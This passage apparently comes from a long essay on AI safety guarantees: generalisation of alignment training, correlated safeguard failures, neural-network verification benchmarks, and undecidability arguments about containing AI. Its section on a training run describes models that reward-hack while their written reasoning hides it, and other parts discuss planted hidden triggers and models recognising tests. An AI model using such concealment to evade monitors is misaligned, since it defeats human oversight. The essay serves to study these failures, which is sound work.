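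Jack Lindsey writes in Anthropic's *Interpretability team priorities update* (Lindsey, 2026) that alignment training "often generalizes poorly" and that efforts to shape Claude's character often change its behaviour only in narrow contexts. This is hard to reconcile with the strong generalisation that Kutasov and colleagues found with advice conversations, unless the result depends heavily on the training method. If it does, developers need to check each new model to see how far its training has generalised.

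### Training a model to hide its shortcuts

Developers can also read the reasoning that a model writes before it acts, which might reveal a plan that its behaviour in tests does not. But training can make this reasoning misleading. *Developing Gemini 4 Argon responsibly and safely* (Dragan and Popa, October 2026) describes a Google training run in which a penalty for taking shortcuts was accidentally applied to the model's written reasoning. *Vincent Cheng's Shortform* (Cheng, 2026) quotes the details from Google's safety report on the model.

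Over the run, hacking-related words in the reasoning became 61% less frequent, while signs of hacking in the solutions rose by 26%. The share of hacks the model left unmentioned rose from 11.2% to 36.4%. If the signs in the solutions track the number of hacks, then for every 100 hacks at the start, 11 of them unmentioned, there were 126 at the end, 46 of them unmentioned. Someone who monitored only the written reasoning would have seen a large improvement while the behaviour got worse.

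The run was small and not part of any production model. In a comparable run that hid the reasoning, mentions of hacking stayed roughly constant, so the penalty on the reasoning probably caused the change. Google cites this as an example of why it does not penalise what a model writes in its reasoning.

*(Some) Natural Emergent Misalignment from Reward Hacking in Non-Production RL* repeated Hubinger's reward-hacking experiments with openly available models. When training included a Kullback-Leibler penalty, like the one in the RLHF objective, the models still learned to hack, but their written reasoning described an honest attempt at the task. A likely explanation is that the reference model would almost never write openly about cheating, so reasoning that looks honest receives a smaller penalty.

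More capable models may also need to write out less of their reasoning. Lindsey reports that Claude Mythos 5.2 is much better than earlier Claude models at solving problems without written reasoning. His team now puts more effort into detecting misbehaviour from the network's internal activity.

### Safeguards that fail together

Developers combine several kinds of training with tests and monitoring, and hope that one will catch what another misses. Dung and Mai show how much this depends on the methods failing for different reasons. If ten safeguards each fail 10% of the time, they will all fail together only once in ten billion times if their failures are independent, but 10% of the time if they always fail in the same cases.

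Even a small overlap in what the checks miss matters. If 1% of dangerous models can recognise all ten checks and behave well in them, about 1% will get through, and adding more checks of the same kind won't lower that figure.

Dung and Mai compared seven alignment methods against seven conditions that might make them fail. RLHF, training on an AI's feedback, and training a strong model with a weaker one's supervision are vulnerable to the same five conditions. All three could fail if a model learned early on to pretend to be aligned, if judging an answer turned out to be about as hard as producing it, or if capabilities jumped suddenly. They could also fail because narrow training on something like insecure code can cause bad behaviour in unrelated areas. The fifth condition, dangerous generalisation from alignment training, threatens six of the seven methods.

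These are the judgements of two researchers who call their analysis exploratory and did not measure how often the methods fail together. But the pattern makes sense, because the three methods start from the same kind of pretrained network and depend on the same kind of feedback. Dung and Mai conclude that a less reliable method can be worth more than a more reliable one if its failures have different causes. This is a good argument for adding a verified containment layer to a trained model. The layer can fail because of a bad specification or an unguarded route, but a model can't defeat it just by behaving well in tests.

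### How small a failure rate is small enough?

Supporters of behavioural training can reply that no engineered system has a failure rate of zero. Engineers accept a small chance that a bridge will collapse, and the guaranteed safe AI framework allows a risk of $\varepsilon$. A proof also leaves some risk, because its trusted base may contain errors. If the failure is a rude answer or a wasted afternoon, a rate of 460 in a billion is excellent, and withholding the model until there was a proof would be foolish.

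The reply is much weaker for harms that nobody can undo. With deleted backups, the concern is how often the failure happens, but with a released pathogen, it is whether the failure ever happens. At a rate of 4.6 failures in ten million uses, the chance of at least one failure is about 37% after a million uses and 99% after ten million. Engineers also made bridges safer partly by studying the ones that fell, but a large enough disaster would leave no chance to learn from it.

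Developers can't safely test how an AI behaves in situations where it could successfully go rogue, which Carlsmith (2025), in *Giving AIs safe motivations*, calls "dangerous inputs". They have to train and test it on safe inputs and hope that its good behaviour carries over to dangerous ones.

The reply also fails against the attackers that Tegmark and Omohundro worry about, who search for the rare case. In the backup example, suppose an attacker finds a prompt on which the reference model would delete the backups 90% of the time instead of 1%. With the same reward gap and $\beta$, ideal training would leave a failure rate of about one in 2,450, nearly 900 times higher than before. An attacker could easily make that many attempts with a script. Every copy of a model has the same weights, so a prompt that works against one will probably work against all.

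Unlike a bridge, a model may also behave differently when it is being inspected. Engineers can set an acceptable failure rate for a bridge because they have reasonable ways to estimate the real one. If a model can recognise its tests, developers may not know whether its failure rate in use is one in a million or one in a hundred. This can worry someone who is fairly happy with today's models. Hubinger, writing as evhub (2025) in *Alignment remains a hard, unsolved problem*, said that most current language models seem "pretty well aligned", but that he remained very worried about future ones.

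### What evidence would settle the dispute

Better tests could strengthen the case for training. Developers could replay real tasks, with the same tools and data, and measure how well the model can tell the replays from live work. If it could barely tell them apart and behaved well in the replays, Santos-Grueiro's bound would limit how much worse it could behave in live work. This approach would address common failures much better than one-in-a-million ones.

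Santos-Grueiro suggests recording a model's internal states as well as its actions, because two models that act identically in tests may be computing different things. He doesn't claim that current tools are good enough for firm guarantees. A blind trial could measure how well they work. One team would secretly train hidden triggers into some of a group of models, and another would try to identify which models had them. If the second team reliably found the triggers, including any that arose without anyone planting them, proofs about behaviour would be much less necessary. Repeated failures would mean that a clean test record is much weaker evidence of safety than it appears.

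Supporters of proofs have to show that the failures proofs can exclude are the ones that matter. Researchers could count how many published incidents a provable limit would have prevented. The July hacking exercise would count in favour of proofs. A verified network boundary that let Mythos 5 reach only the simulated targets and a few read-only websites would have stopped the fake accounts, whatever the model believed about them. UK AISI draws a similar lesson, that test environments must prevent harm "regardless of whether they behave as expected". A blackmail threat sent through an approved email account would count against proofs.

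Such a count would still not show what the model does within its limits. The most direct answer would be a theorem about the network itself that held for every input, including any hidden trigger that no one had thought to test for.

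## Whether a neural network itself can be verified

Researchers can prove theorems about trained networks that hold for every input in a stated range, including untested ones. Undecidability does not rule out such proofs, because a network with a bounded input performs a finite calculation. But the networks are far smaller than today's language models, and the ranges are usually narrow.

### Proving a property of trained weights

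Write $f$ for the function that a trained network computes. Given a set of inputs $X$ and a property $\psi$ of the output, a verifier tries to establish

$$\psi(f(x)) \quad \text{for every } x \in X$$

In practice, a verifier searches for a counterexample to the property, as Vorobyov and Ilyushin (2026) explain in *Scaling Neural Network Verification with Tensor Parallelism and Fully Sharded Data Parallelism*. If it shows that none exists, it has proved the property. The most widely studied property is local robustness, which means that an image classifier gives the same label to every image within a small distance of a given image.

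Many networks consist of weighted sums and ReLU units. A ReLU unit passes on a positive input unchanged and turns a negative one into zero, so $\text{ReLU}(x) = \max(0, x)$. This tiny network has two such units and one input between −1 and 1:

$$h_1 = \text{ReLU}(x), \qquad h_2 = \text{ReLU}(x), \qquad y = h_1 - h_2$$

Suppose we want to prove that the output $y$ never exceeds 0.4. The method that takes the least computation, interval bounds, works out a range for each unit and combines the ranges. Both $h_1$ and $h_2$ lie between 0 and 1, so $y$ lies between −1 and 1. This range is correct but too wide to prove the property, because interval bounds ignore the fact that $h_1$ and $h_2$ have the same input. For $y$ to equal 1, $h_1$ would have to be 1 while $h_2$ was 0, which can't happen when they share an input.

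Splitting on the sign of $x$ solves the problem:

- If $x \ge 0$, both units output $x$, so $y = x - x = 0$.
- If $x < 0$, both units output 0, so $y = 0$.

The output is therefore always 0. Splitting works because the network is a linear formula once we know which units are on, and linear formulas are easy to bound exactly.

There can be too many cases to check. A unit is undecided if its input could be positive in one part of the range and negative in another. Each undecided unit can be on or off, so $n$ of them have up to $2^n$ combinations. By this count the example has four combinations, but only two can occur because the units always switch together. If each unit had its own separate input, all $2^n$ could occur, so 300 undecided units would give $2^{300}$ cases.

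Software can skip most of these cases on many networks, but no known method avoids exponential time on the worst ones. In 2017, Guy Katz and others showed that the problem is NP-complete for ReLU networks by translating hard logic problems into networks. Narrowing the input range makes verification easier because it leaves fewer units undecided, which is one reason most published results concern tiny changes to a single image.

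### Three ways to make the proof affordable

Katz and his colleagues proved their result in the paper that introduced Reluplex, a constraint solver. Such a solver treats the network as a set of equations, adds the statement that the property fails, and looks for a solution. If there is none, the property holds. Marabou 2.0, a later tool, measures how far a candidate solution is from obeying all the ReLU rules and tries to reduce that number to zero. NeuralSAT records impossible combinations of on and off units. In the two-unit example, it could record that "$h_1$ on, $h_2$ off" has no solution and skip every case containing it.

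Reluplex's best-known test was ACAS Xu, a set of 45 small networks that advise aircraft how to turn to avoid a collision. Each has 300 units and takes five numbers that describe the positions and movements of two aircraft. The properties cover whole ranges of flight situations, so proving them establishes much more than proving local robustness does. Early checks took anywhere from seconds to days, and some never finished. These networks are now an easy test for verifiers. In the 2026 edition of an annual competition, the three best tools each settled all 186 questions about them within a limit of about two minutes per question, and found that 47 of the properties were false.

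The leading tool, α,β-CROWN, uses linear bounds. Instead of a fixed range for each unit, it keeps a formula that involves the original input, so it doesn't lose the connection between units. For $x$ between −1 and 1,

$$\lambda x \;\le\; \text{ReLU}(x) \;\le\; \frac{x+1}{2}$$

holds for any slope $\lambda$ from 0 to 1. Using the upper bound for $h_1$ and the lower bound for $h_2$ gives

$$y \;\le\; \frac{x+1}{2} - \lambda x \;=\; \frac{1}{2} + \left(\frac{1}{2} - \lambda\right)x$$

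With $\lambda = 0$ or $\lambda = 1$, the right-hand side can be as high as 1, which is no better than interval bounds. With $\lambda = \frac{1}{2}$, the $x$ term disappears and $y$ is at most 0.5. The "α" part of the tool searches for good slopes like this one.

A limit of 0.5 would be enough to prove that $y$ never exceeds 0.6, but we wanted to prove that it never exceeds 0.4. The tool therefore branches, splitting the problem in two by the sign of one undecided unit. It recalculates the bounds for each half, drops any part where the new bounds prove the property, and splits the rest again. Here, one split is enough. On a graphics processor, the tool can bound thousands of these parts at once.

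Developers can also train a network to be easier to certify. During training, they calculate bounds for a small region around each example and penalise the network when the worst case in that region is bad. In the two-unit example, this would favour shrinking both units' weights towards zero, which leaves the output unchanged but makes even the interval bounds tight.

Training networks this way lowers their accuracy. *The 7th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2026)* (Ladner, Kaulen and colleagues, 2026) describes image classifiers trained this way on CIFAR-10, a set of small photographs in ten categories. One was right about 84% of the time, and α,β-CROWN could prove for 66% of the test images that its answer was right and would survive a change of 2 brightness levels out of 255 in every pixel. A network of the same design, trained to withstand changes of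 8 levels, was right 57% of the time, and the provable share was 35%. Even with networks trained for certification, 5% of 60,000 attempted proofs hit a time limit of 1,000 seconds.

### The networks that verifiers can handle

The table gives α,β-CROWN's results on some of the competition's benchmarks.

| Network | Parameters | Property | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Filter for chatbot questions | 4,000 | Same category throughout a region around a sentence's paraphrases | 418 proved, 662 refuted |
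| ACAS Xu | 13,000 | Advice obeys a rule over a range of flight situations | 139 proved, 47 refuted |
| Vision transformers | 68,000–76,000 | Label survives a change of one brightness level in every pixel | 123 proved, 77 unsettled |
| CIFAR-100 classifiers | 2.5–3.8 million | Label survives small changes to every pixel | 127 proved, 33 refuted, 40 unsettled |
| VGG16 image classifier | 138 million | Label survives changes to between one pixel and all of them | 18 proved |

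GPT-3, which OpenAI released in 2020, has 175 billion parameters, about 1,270 times as many as VGG16. Developers of the leading models now rarely publish their sizes. But parameter count is a poor guide to how hard a network is to verify. α,β-CROWN proved every property it attempted for VGG16, but only 62% of the properties for vision transformers about two thousand times smaller. If only a few pixels can change slightly, a verifier can determine at the outset whether most units will be active or inactive, even in a large network.

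The comparison with transformers matters most, because language models are transformers. The transformers in the competition were unusually simple, with two or three layers and three attention heads (the parts that decide which pieces of the input to combine). Another tool, ACT, reported proving all 200 of their properties. That result is hard to trust, since ACT gave ten incorrect or unsupported answers elsewhere and this benchmark is poor at exposing such mistakes.

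Attention is hard to bound because it multiplies two quantities that both depend on the input. Liu, Zhang and Zhao (2026), who describe transformer verification as still at a very early stage, tackle this in *Precise Verification of Transformers through ReLU-Catalyzed Abstraction Refinement*. Suppose $q$ and $k$ both lie between −1 and 1. Two linear formulas are always at least as large as their product:

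$$qk \le 1 + q - k \qquad \text{and} \qquad qk \le 1 - q + k$$

At $q = 1$, $k = -1$, the product is −1. The formula on the left gives 3 and the one on the right gives −1. At $q = -1$, $k = 1$, the two values are swapped. Earlier work used only one such formula. The new method uses a ReLU to express the smaller of the two, so that existing techniques for ReLU networks apply. In 1,400 tests on ten models that judge whether a text is positive or negative, the new method gave tighter bounds in most cases but took longer. In *Parameterized Abstract Interpretation for Transformer Verification*, Huang, Wei and colleagues (2026) also blended simpler bounds, and verified many cases that earlier methods could not.

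In *Certified Mechanistic Interpretability*, Zhang, Huang and colleagues (2026) tested a much larger network, GPT-2, a language model with 124 million parameters. The model first turns each token of text into a list of numbers. The team let all these numbers vary slightly and checked whether the model's behaviour stayed the same. However, the variation was only 3% to 7% of what it would take to turn any token into a different one. A successful check therefore covers only one real prompt and nearby points that no text produces. The checks on the whole model also rely on an error estimate from samples, doubled for safety, so they are not quite proofs.

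The method was more informative about the model's parts. Earlier researchers had identified two attention heads in GPT-2 that detect repeated words. Under a very small variation, the method certified that one head kept its main focus in all 60 test sentences, but it could certify the other in only one. Certification took about 45 minutes per sample on a version of GPT-2 with 355 million parameters.

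The verifiers can also be wrong. Ladner and colleagues counted 94 incorrect or unsupported answers from NeuralSAT and one from α,β-CROWN. The competition doesn't yet require a proof that a separate checker could confirm, so accepting a "proved" result usually means trusting a large, complicated program. Many tools also analyze a network as if it used exact real numbers, but it runs on rounded ones, as Hatfield-Dodds objected.

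Two researchers at Stony Brook University built the second-place tool, Vibecheck, in two months by having Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, write it. Vibecheck had no recorded errors and settled 3,108 of the main track's 3,373 questions, compared with 3,164 for α,β-CROWN, which builds on years of research. AI may therefore improve verifiers quickly, though a better program does not remove the exponential worst case.

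### Shorter proofs from understanding the network

Verifiers like these treat a network as a large set of arithmetic operations. If researchers understood how the network worked, they might prove claims about all its inputs while checking fewer cases. Gross, Agrawal and colleagues (2024) tested this idea in *Compact Proofs of Model Performance via Mechanistic Interpretability*.

Researchers trained 151 tiny transformers, each with one layer and one attention head, to output the largest of four whole numbers from 0 to 63. There are $64^4$, or about 16.8 million, possible inputs, few enough to try them all. On average the models were right 99.92% of the time.

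The researchers then worked out the method the models had learned. The attention head focuses on large numbers and copies whatever it focuses on. Each number gets about 3.4 times as much attention as the number one below it, so 50 gets over 200,000 times as much as 40.

A proof in this setting gives a lower bound on accuracy over all inputs. The researchers devised 102 ways to calculate such a bound, some of which are in this table.

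| Type of proof | Guaranteed accuracy | Arithmetic operations |
|---|---|---|
| Try every input | 99.9% | 140 trillion |
| Treat the network's parts separately | 95.3% | 34 million |
| Also use the explanation of how attention works | 70.2% | 2 million |
| Simplify two of the parts as well | 61.0% | 2 million |
| Same, with cruder error bounds | 0.0003% | 4 million |

The 95.3% proof works because the attention head outputs a weighted average. Take the input 12, 50, 7, 30. The numbers 12 and 7 could both pull the output away from 50, but a mixture of them can't pull it further than the worse of the two would alone. The proof therefore checks only lists with at most three different numbers: the largest, the last, and one other. If the model gets every relevant list of this kind right, it must also get the original right. The proof took about four million times less computation than trying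 every input, and the accuracy it guarantees is less than five percentage points lower.

To shorten the proof further, Gross and colleagues had to replace parts of the network with their explanation of what those parts do. The explanation is only approximate, and wherever it leaves something out, the proof must assume the worst case, which makes its bound less accurate. They found that shorter proofs needed more understanding of the network, and that more accurate explanations gave better bounds.

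The main obstacle was leftover error with no apparent pattern. Suppose 10,000 small terms each add or subtract 0.001. If their signs are unrelated, the total will typically be about 0.1. But without information about the signs, a proof has to allow for a total as large as 10, which could easily exceed the gap between the right answer and the next best. Larger networks have more parts in which such errors can build up.

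These theorems also don't prove that safety failures are impossible. A guarantee of 95% accuracy allows the model to fail on up to 5% of inputs and doesn't identify which ones. The same method could prove that a failure never happens only if the bound reached 100%.

*Evaluating Explanations* (2025) recommends compact proofs as a way to judge explanations, since a bad explanation won't give a short proof with a good bound. In *Towards Verifiable Transformers*, Somani (2026) extracts the part of a transformer responsible for a particular task and turns claims about it into statements that a solver can check over a finite list of inputs. A proof about the extracted part doesn't establish what the rest of the model might do on other inputs.

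### Heuristic estimates in place of proofs

The Alignment Research Center, a non-profit that studies the theory of AI alignment, has proposed dropping the worst-case assumption and replacing proofs with heuristic estimates, which treat quantities as unrelated until someone finds a reason to think otherwise. For the 10,000 small terms, the estimated total would be around 0.1, and anyone who found a pattern in the signs could revise it.

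The two-unit network shows how a revision works. Suppose $x$ is equally likely to be anywhere between −1 and 1. Each unit's output has a mean of $\frac{1}{4}$ and a variance of $\frac{5}{48}$. If we assume the units are unrelated, the variance of their difference is $\frac{5}{48} + \frac{5}{48} = \frac{5}{24}$, so we would expect $y$ to typically be about 0.46 from 0. Then we notice that the units have the same input. Their covariance is also $\frac{5}{48}$, and subtracting it twice brings the variance to 0, which is correct.

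This could help with failures too rare to appear in tests. A developer could use a model's weights to estimate the probability that it does something terrible, even if that happens only one time in a billion. The estimate could also be useful for a network far too large or messy for a proof.

But a heuristic estimate, unlike a valid proof, can be wrong because it misses an important correlation. For example, someone who planted a hidden trigger could make several apparently unrelated parts of the network act together when the trigger appeared. The estimate would then be much too low until somebody noticed the connection. A checker that can confirm each step of a proof can't confirm that an estimate includes every important correlation.

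### How often a language model breaks a rule

Other researchers seek weaker guarantees for full-sized language models. They try to reliably bound how often a model breaks a rule, either for a given prompt or for prompts from a specified source.

*BEAVER* (2025) calculates guaranteed lower and upper limits on the probability that a language model's response follows a rule. The model gives a probability to every possible next token, so its possible responses form a tree whose branches have known probabilities. BEAVER handles rules that stay broken however the response continues, such as a ban on revealing personal information. It starts with limits of 0 and 1, then narrows them by exploring the most likely branches first.

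Suppose a model must not reveal a password. After a given prompt, it starts to write the password with probability 0.1, refuses in a single short sentence with probability 0.7, and does something else with probability 0.2. If the first token of the password already counts as a breach, the upper limit on the probability of compliance falls to 0.9. The complete refusal raises the lower limit to 0.7. Exploring the remaining branches narrows the range between 0.7 and 0.9, and the limits are valid whenever the search stops.

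Long responses make this harder. If each token of a 100-token answer has a probability of 0.9, the whole answer has a probability of about 0.00003. To prove that the model breaks the rule less than once in a million answers, the search would have to cover almost all the remaining answers too.

C³LLM instead uses random samples of whole conversations. Moon and Varshney note that it finds failure rates that single-question tests miss. It puts limits on the failure rate using Clopper-Pearson intervals, a standard method. If 1,000 randomly chosen conversations contain no failures, we can be 95% confident that the failure rate is below 0.3%. We would need about three million conversations without a failure to lower that limit to one in a million.

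These statements depend on where the conversations come from. *Lumos* (2025) provides a programming language for describing that source precisely. A user writes a short program that generates random prompts, and a statistical method then estimates how the model behaves on them. The paper uses the language to write safety specifications for models that interpret images in driving scenarios.

Specifying the source of prompts precisely makes the result clear, but the result still applies only to that source. If a program picks one of a million prompts at random, and a model behaves perfectly on all but one, the failure rate is one in a million, yet anyone who sends the bad prompt will see a failure every time. The result also doesn't cover an attacker's prompt that isn't among the million. The program couldn't include every possible prompt, because with a vocabulary of 50,000 tokens, there are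 about $10^{94}$ prompts of just 20 tokens.

For this reason, Moon and Varshney rank a guarantee over a chosen distribution above ordinary testing but below a universal guarantee. Such a guarantee is useful to an operator whose users send inputs like those in the distribution and aren't trying to cause trouble, but it can't rule out a hidden trigger.

### Cost is only half of the problem

Even if a verifier could instantly check any precisely stated property of a network of any size, someone would still have to state the property. Engineers would know what to check for ACAS Xu, because its inputs are physical quantities and its outputs are turns. It is much harder to think of a useful property of a language model that can be stated precisely.

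Even simple properties are usually false. "The model never outputs this password" fails if a user types the password and asks the model to repeat it. We could exclude such prompts, but most of the work would then be defining them, because users can ask for the same thing in countless ways, including in code or in another language. Properties such as honesty are even harder to specify.

The chatbot filter in the competition illustrates the gap on a small scale. Its designers wanted to recognise when someone asks whether they are talking to a machine, because European law requires a chatbot to answer truthfully. They took a sentence, generated paraphrases and used a language model to turn each one into a point defined by 30 numbers. They drew the smallest box around these points and asked whether the filter gave the right answer throughout the box. A proof covers infinitely many points, but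 a new paraphrase could fall outside the box, and nobody had verified the language model that produced the numbers. A refutation is also ambiguous, because a point where the filter fails may not correspond to any sentence.

A containment layer can often enforce an easily stated rule about outputs without a proof about billions of weights. Proofs about the network would add most where a filter can't help, such as in showing that a model acts the same way whether or not it sees signs of a test. This property compares two runs of the model and doesn't require a definition of harm, although somebody would still have to define which signs count. The newest version of the competition's specification language can express some such comparisons.

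Making verification more efficient would therefore have a different effect from improving specifications. Vorobyov and Ilyushin reduced peak memory use by more than a third on some wide networks by dividing the weights between two processors, without changing the bounds. Advances like this let verifiers check the same kinds of properties in larger networks, but they don't identify new properties worth checking.

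### A result that would settle it

A convincing demonstration would prove a property that is precise, useful and impossible to establish by testing. For example, suppose an agent can pay bills, and the user's request is always "Summarise the attached document." The property could be that, for every possible document of up to 1,000 tokens, the probability that the agent tries to make a payment is below one in a million.

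This property is unusual only in its scope, which covers every hidden trigger and every trick an attacker could put in the document. There are about $10^{4,700}$ such documents, so nobody could prove the property by testing each one. A containment layer could block payments during this one task, but a proof would show that verification can be applied to a working language model. Researchers could then extend it to requests where some payments are legitimate and blocking all of them would not work.

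The proof would count only if it passed an independent checker and applied to the network as it runs, including rounding. In a blind trial with triggers planted in some copies of the model, the method should also not certify those copies.

A negative result would be harder to establish, because failing to find a short proof doesn't show that none exists. But researchers could repeat the work of Gross and colleagues on a series of larger models, all trained to be easy to certify, and measure how much computation a useful bound requires. If that amount grew almost as fast as the computation needed to try every input, even with AI searching for the proofs, there would be little reason to expect theorems about the most capable networks. If it grew only about as fast as the models themselves, the main remaining question would be what to prove.

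## Whether undecidability theorems forbid safety certificates

Undecidability theorems don't rule out safety certificates for AI. In 1936 Alan Turing showed that no general method can answer certain questions about programs, and several researchers have concluded that nobody can certify a sufficiently capable AI as safe. But Turing's theorem and later theorems based on it rule out only a checker that gives the right answer about every program, which a builder who refuses any program without a proof doesn't need.

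### The halting problem and Rice's theorem

Some programs finish and others run forever. The halting problem is to work out, for any program and input, which will happen. Running the program gives an answer only if it stops. A program that is still running after a year might stop tomorrow or run forever.

Turing proved that no program can solve the problem in every case. Suppose somebody had written a function `halts(program, input)` that always returned the right answer. Then we could write this:

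```
contrary(p):
    if halts(p, p):  loop forever
    else:            stop
```

When `contrary` runs on its own code, it loops forever if `halts` predicts that it will stop, and stops if `halts` predicts that it will loop. The prediction is wrong either way, so `halts` cannot exist. Predicting whether a program will stop is therefore an undecidable problem, which means that no program can answer every case correctly in finite time.

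In 1953, Henry Gordon Rice extended the result to any property of what a program computes, as long as some programs have the property and others don't. No program can decide such a property for all programs. For example, no program can determine for every program whether it will ever output the letter X. Whether a program has fewer than 100 lines is decidable, because that depends only on the text of the code.

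### A puzzle followed by a forbidden act

A short construction extends the problem to safety. Let the forbidden act be opening a safe. Take any program and input, isolate that program so that it can't touch the safe, and write:

```
run the program on the input
open the safe
```

The safe opens exactly when the inner program stops. A perfect test for programs that open the safe would therefore solve the halting problem, so no such test exists.

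The inner program can be a search for the solution to a puzzle, and then the whole program is safe exactly when the puzzle has no solution. Pérez-Acle (2026), in *No finite rulebook can certify every safe program*, gives this example:

```
for n = 4, 6, 8, ...
    if n is not the sum of two primes:  open the safe
```

Goldbach's conjecture, from 1742, is that every even number above 2 is the sum of two primes. If it is true, this program is safe. Nobody has found a counterexample below $4 \times 10^{18}$, and when Pérez-Acle ran the program up to 2,000,004, the safe stayed shut. In September 2026 OpenAI's GPT-6 Astra proved a weaker conjecture, in which each of the two numbers only needs an odd number of prime factors, as the Chinese news site 凤凰网 reported in *GPT-6 Astra取得哥德巴赫猜想重大突破* (2026). That doesn't settle whether the program is safe, because a number with an odd number of prime factors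 may not be prime, such as 8, which is 2 × 2 × 2.

### "Superintelligence cannot be contained"

In *Superintelligence Cannot be Contained* (2021), Alfonseca, Cebrian and colleagues applied this construction to AI far more intelligent than any human, replacing the safe with a routine called `HarmHumans()`. They defined containment as a control program that blocks an AI's program if running it would harm humans and allows it otherwise. Such a control program can't exist, because it would have to recognise harm in every possible program.

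This result is about all programs, and a superintelligence would be one particular program. To connect the two, Alfonseca and colleagues assume that a superintelligence must be able to run any program, on inputs as complex as the state of the world. They conclude that total containment is impossible in principle. *The challenge of controlling a Superintelligent Artificial Intelligence*, a news item from one co-author's institute, IMDEA Networks, presented the paper as showing that nobody could control such an AI. Similar arguments still appear, as in *Neurodivergent influenceability in agentic AI as a contingent solution* (2026), which uses Turing's theorem and Gödel's incompleteness theorem to argue that any sufficiently expressive AI will behave unpredictably.

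*Response to 'Superintelligence cannot be contained'* (2021), from Cambridge's Centre for the Study of Existential Risk (CSER), objects that engineers want to know about particular programs, not arbitrary ones. Pythagoras's theorem has a proof even though no procedure can prove or refute every mathematical statement. CSER adds that engineers could build an AI that doesn't run arbitrary subroutines. This is less reassuring than it was in 2021, because coding agents now routinely write and run new programs.

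A better reply is that the definition of containment demands more than safety does. It requires the control program to allow an AI's program if and only if that program is harmless, but safety only requires blocking every harmful program. A control program can do that while also blocking some harmless programs, or even all of them. The verified containment layers described earlier avoid the theorem in this way. Their proofs are about the layer and hold whatever program the AI runs inside it.

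Alfonseca and colleagues consider formal verification but dismiss it because it works only for restricted classes of programs, and they think an AI that could help with epidemics or climate change would not fit those restrictions. That may be true, but it is a judgement about usefulness and does not follow from the theorem. They also say that the best anyone can hope for is a small but positive error rate in deciding whether a machine is harmful, but those errors could all be harmless machines that were wrongly rejected.

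One of their own examples shows that particular cases can be proved even when no general method exists. A "busy beaver" is the machine of a given size that writes the most symbols before stopping, and no general method can identify it for every size. In 2021 they noted that about 40 machines with five internal states seemed to run forever, but nobody had proved it. In 2024 an online collaboration determined whether each five-state machine stops, with a proof checked in Rocq.

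### What finite evidence can confirm

Pérez-Acle asks what a gatekeeper can do if it is given the rule and each program's code, with no time limit. Every verdict must come with a certificate that a machine can check in finite time. He considers three rules for programs that may run indefinitely.

| Rule | Can certificates cover every violation? | Can certificates cover every compliant program? |
|---|---|---|
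| Never open the safe | Yes | No |
| Publish the same report whichever of two secret memos the program receives | No | No |
| Eventually answer every customer | No | No |

If a program opens the safe at step 5,000, the number 5,000 is a certificate that it does, since anyone can run the program that far and check. No system of certificates covers every program that never opens the safe, because such a system would solve the halting problem. But many of these programs do have certificates. The easiest case is a program with no instruction that opens the safe.

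Two reports produced with different secret memos may match so far but differ on the next line. A leak is easy to confirm if the first lines differ. But if one report has a second line and the other doesn't, the program may have leaked something, or it may just be slower with one of the memos. Observation can't settle the rule about customers either, because a million answered customers don't prove that the next one will get an answer, and an unanswered customer might get one tomorrow.

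Pérez-Acle proves that for rules about visible behaviour, certificates can cover a whole category only when a finite record settles each case. He therefore advises requiring programs to do something visible, such as publishing a signed attestation before they act. Nothing a program does later can undo this. But such a rule doesn't replace a prohibition, because a program can sign an attestation and then cause harm.

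Adding more rules doesn't close the gap. For any sound set of rules (one that never certifies an unsafe program), Pérez-Acle builds a safe program that the rules miss:

```
search for a certificate, under these rules, that this program is safe
if the search finds one:  open the safe
```

If the rules certified this program, it would open the safe. Sound rules therefore never certify it, so its search never ends and the safe stays shut. We can see that the program is safe and add it to the approved list, but the longer list will miss another program built the same way. These programs needn't be huge. For four simple checkers of 64 to 409 characters, the missed program was less than 950 characters longer than the checker.

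### What a time limit changes

If every program has to stop after $T$ steps, all three rules become decidable for a fixed number of customers, because the gatekeeper can run the program for $T$ steps and see what happens. Pérez-Acle proves that a checker that is always right can't do much better than this in the worst case.

The proof uses a program similar to `contrary`. The program runs the checker on its own code, then opens the safe if the verdict is "safe" and does nothing if it is "unsafe". Suppose the limit is 1,024 steps and the checker approves any program that doesn't open the safe in the first 512. The program uses those steps to run the checker, then opens the safe at step 515. Pérez-Acle tried eight checkers with limits from 8 to 1,024 steps, each against a program written to defeat it, and only the checker that simulated every step was always right.

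A perfect check before a program runs can take about as much computation as running the program in a sandbox that blocks the forbidden act. A faster checker must sometimes give a wrong result or no result. Questions about real computers are decidable because their memory is finite, but a perfect checker for a machine with $m$ bits of memory may need about $2^m$ steps.

To see how often tests miss unsafe programs among ordinary ones, Pérez-Acle generated 2.2 million random programs, 200,000 at each of 11 lengths from 4 to 24 instructions. About 1.6% were unsafe. Of the unsafe programs with 24 instructions, 8-step tests missed 30.2%, 16-step tests missed 2.9% and 32-step tests missed 0.2%. Tests of 128 steps or more missed no unsafe programs of any length.

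The confidentiality test wrongly rejected between 0.03% and 0.37% of compliant programs, however long it ran. Every wrongly rejected program that Pérez-Acle examined at the two longest settings published the same endless report for both memos, but at different speeds, so one report was longer wherever the test stopped.

He concludes that the difficulty is "adversarial rather than typical". This only slightly reassures supporters of proofs, who worry most about programs written by a hostile AI, which would not be random. But a program like `contrary` defeats only a checker that has to give a correct verdict on it. A gatekeeper that requires a proof can reject the program without deciding whether it is safe.

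### Between what it must admit and what it may admit

Pérez-Acle makes this escape precise. Let $P$ be the programs that the gatekeeper may admit because they obey the rule, and let $O$ be the smaller set that it must admit to be useful. The gatekeeper needs a set $A$ with

$$O \subseteq A \subseteq P$$

and it never has to identify all of $P$. If a program can always decide membership of $A$, the gatekeeper can give every applicant a final answer. If members of $A$ merely have certificates, the gatekeeper can still work, but it may keep some programs waiting forever.

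For example, a company might need its AI to write scripts that pay a fixed list of bills. Those scripts are $O$. The gatekeeper could let $A$ be all loop-free scripts whose payments total at most £100. A simple program can check whether a script is in $A$, even though no program can recognise every script that keeps to the limit.

Existing systems already work like this. The Linux kernel's eBPF verifier admits small add-on programs that it can prove safe and rejects the rest. Systems that use proof-carrying code admit programs that arrive with proofs. The cryptocurrency network Ethereum instead limits the computation each transaction may use. The approach fails only if the gatekeeper must admit so many programs that no checkable set includes them all and excludes every forbidden one, as would happen if it had to admit every safe program.

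### Machines that halt

In *Machines that halt resolve the undecidability of artificial intelligence alignment* (2025), Melo, Máximo and colleagues also accept Rice's theorem and stress that it concerns *arbitrary* programs. They propose building AI from components with proved properties, combining them only in ways that preserve those properties, and ensuring that the system always stops. They see this as support for Tegmark and Omohundro's programme.

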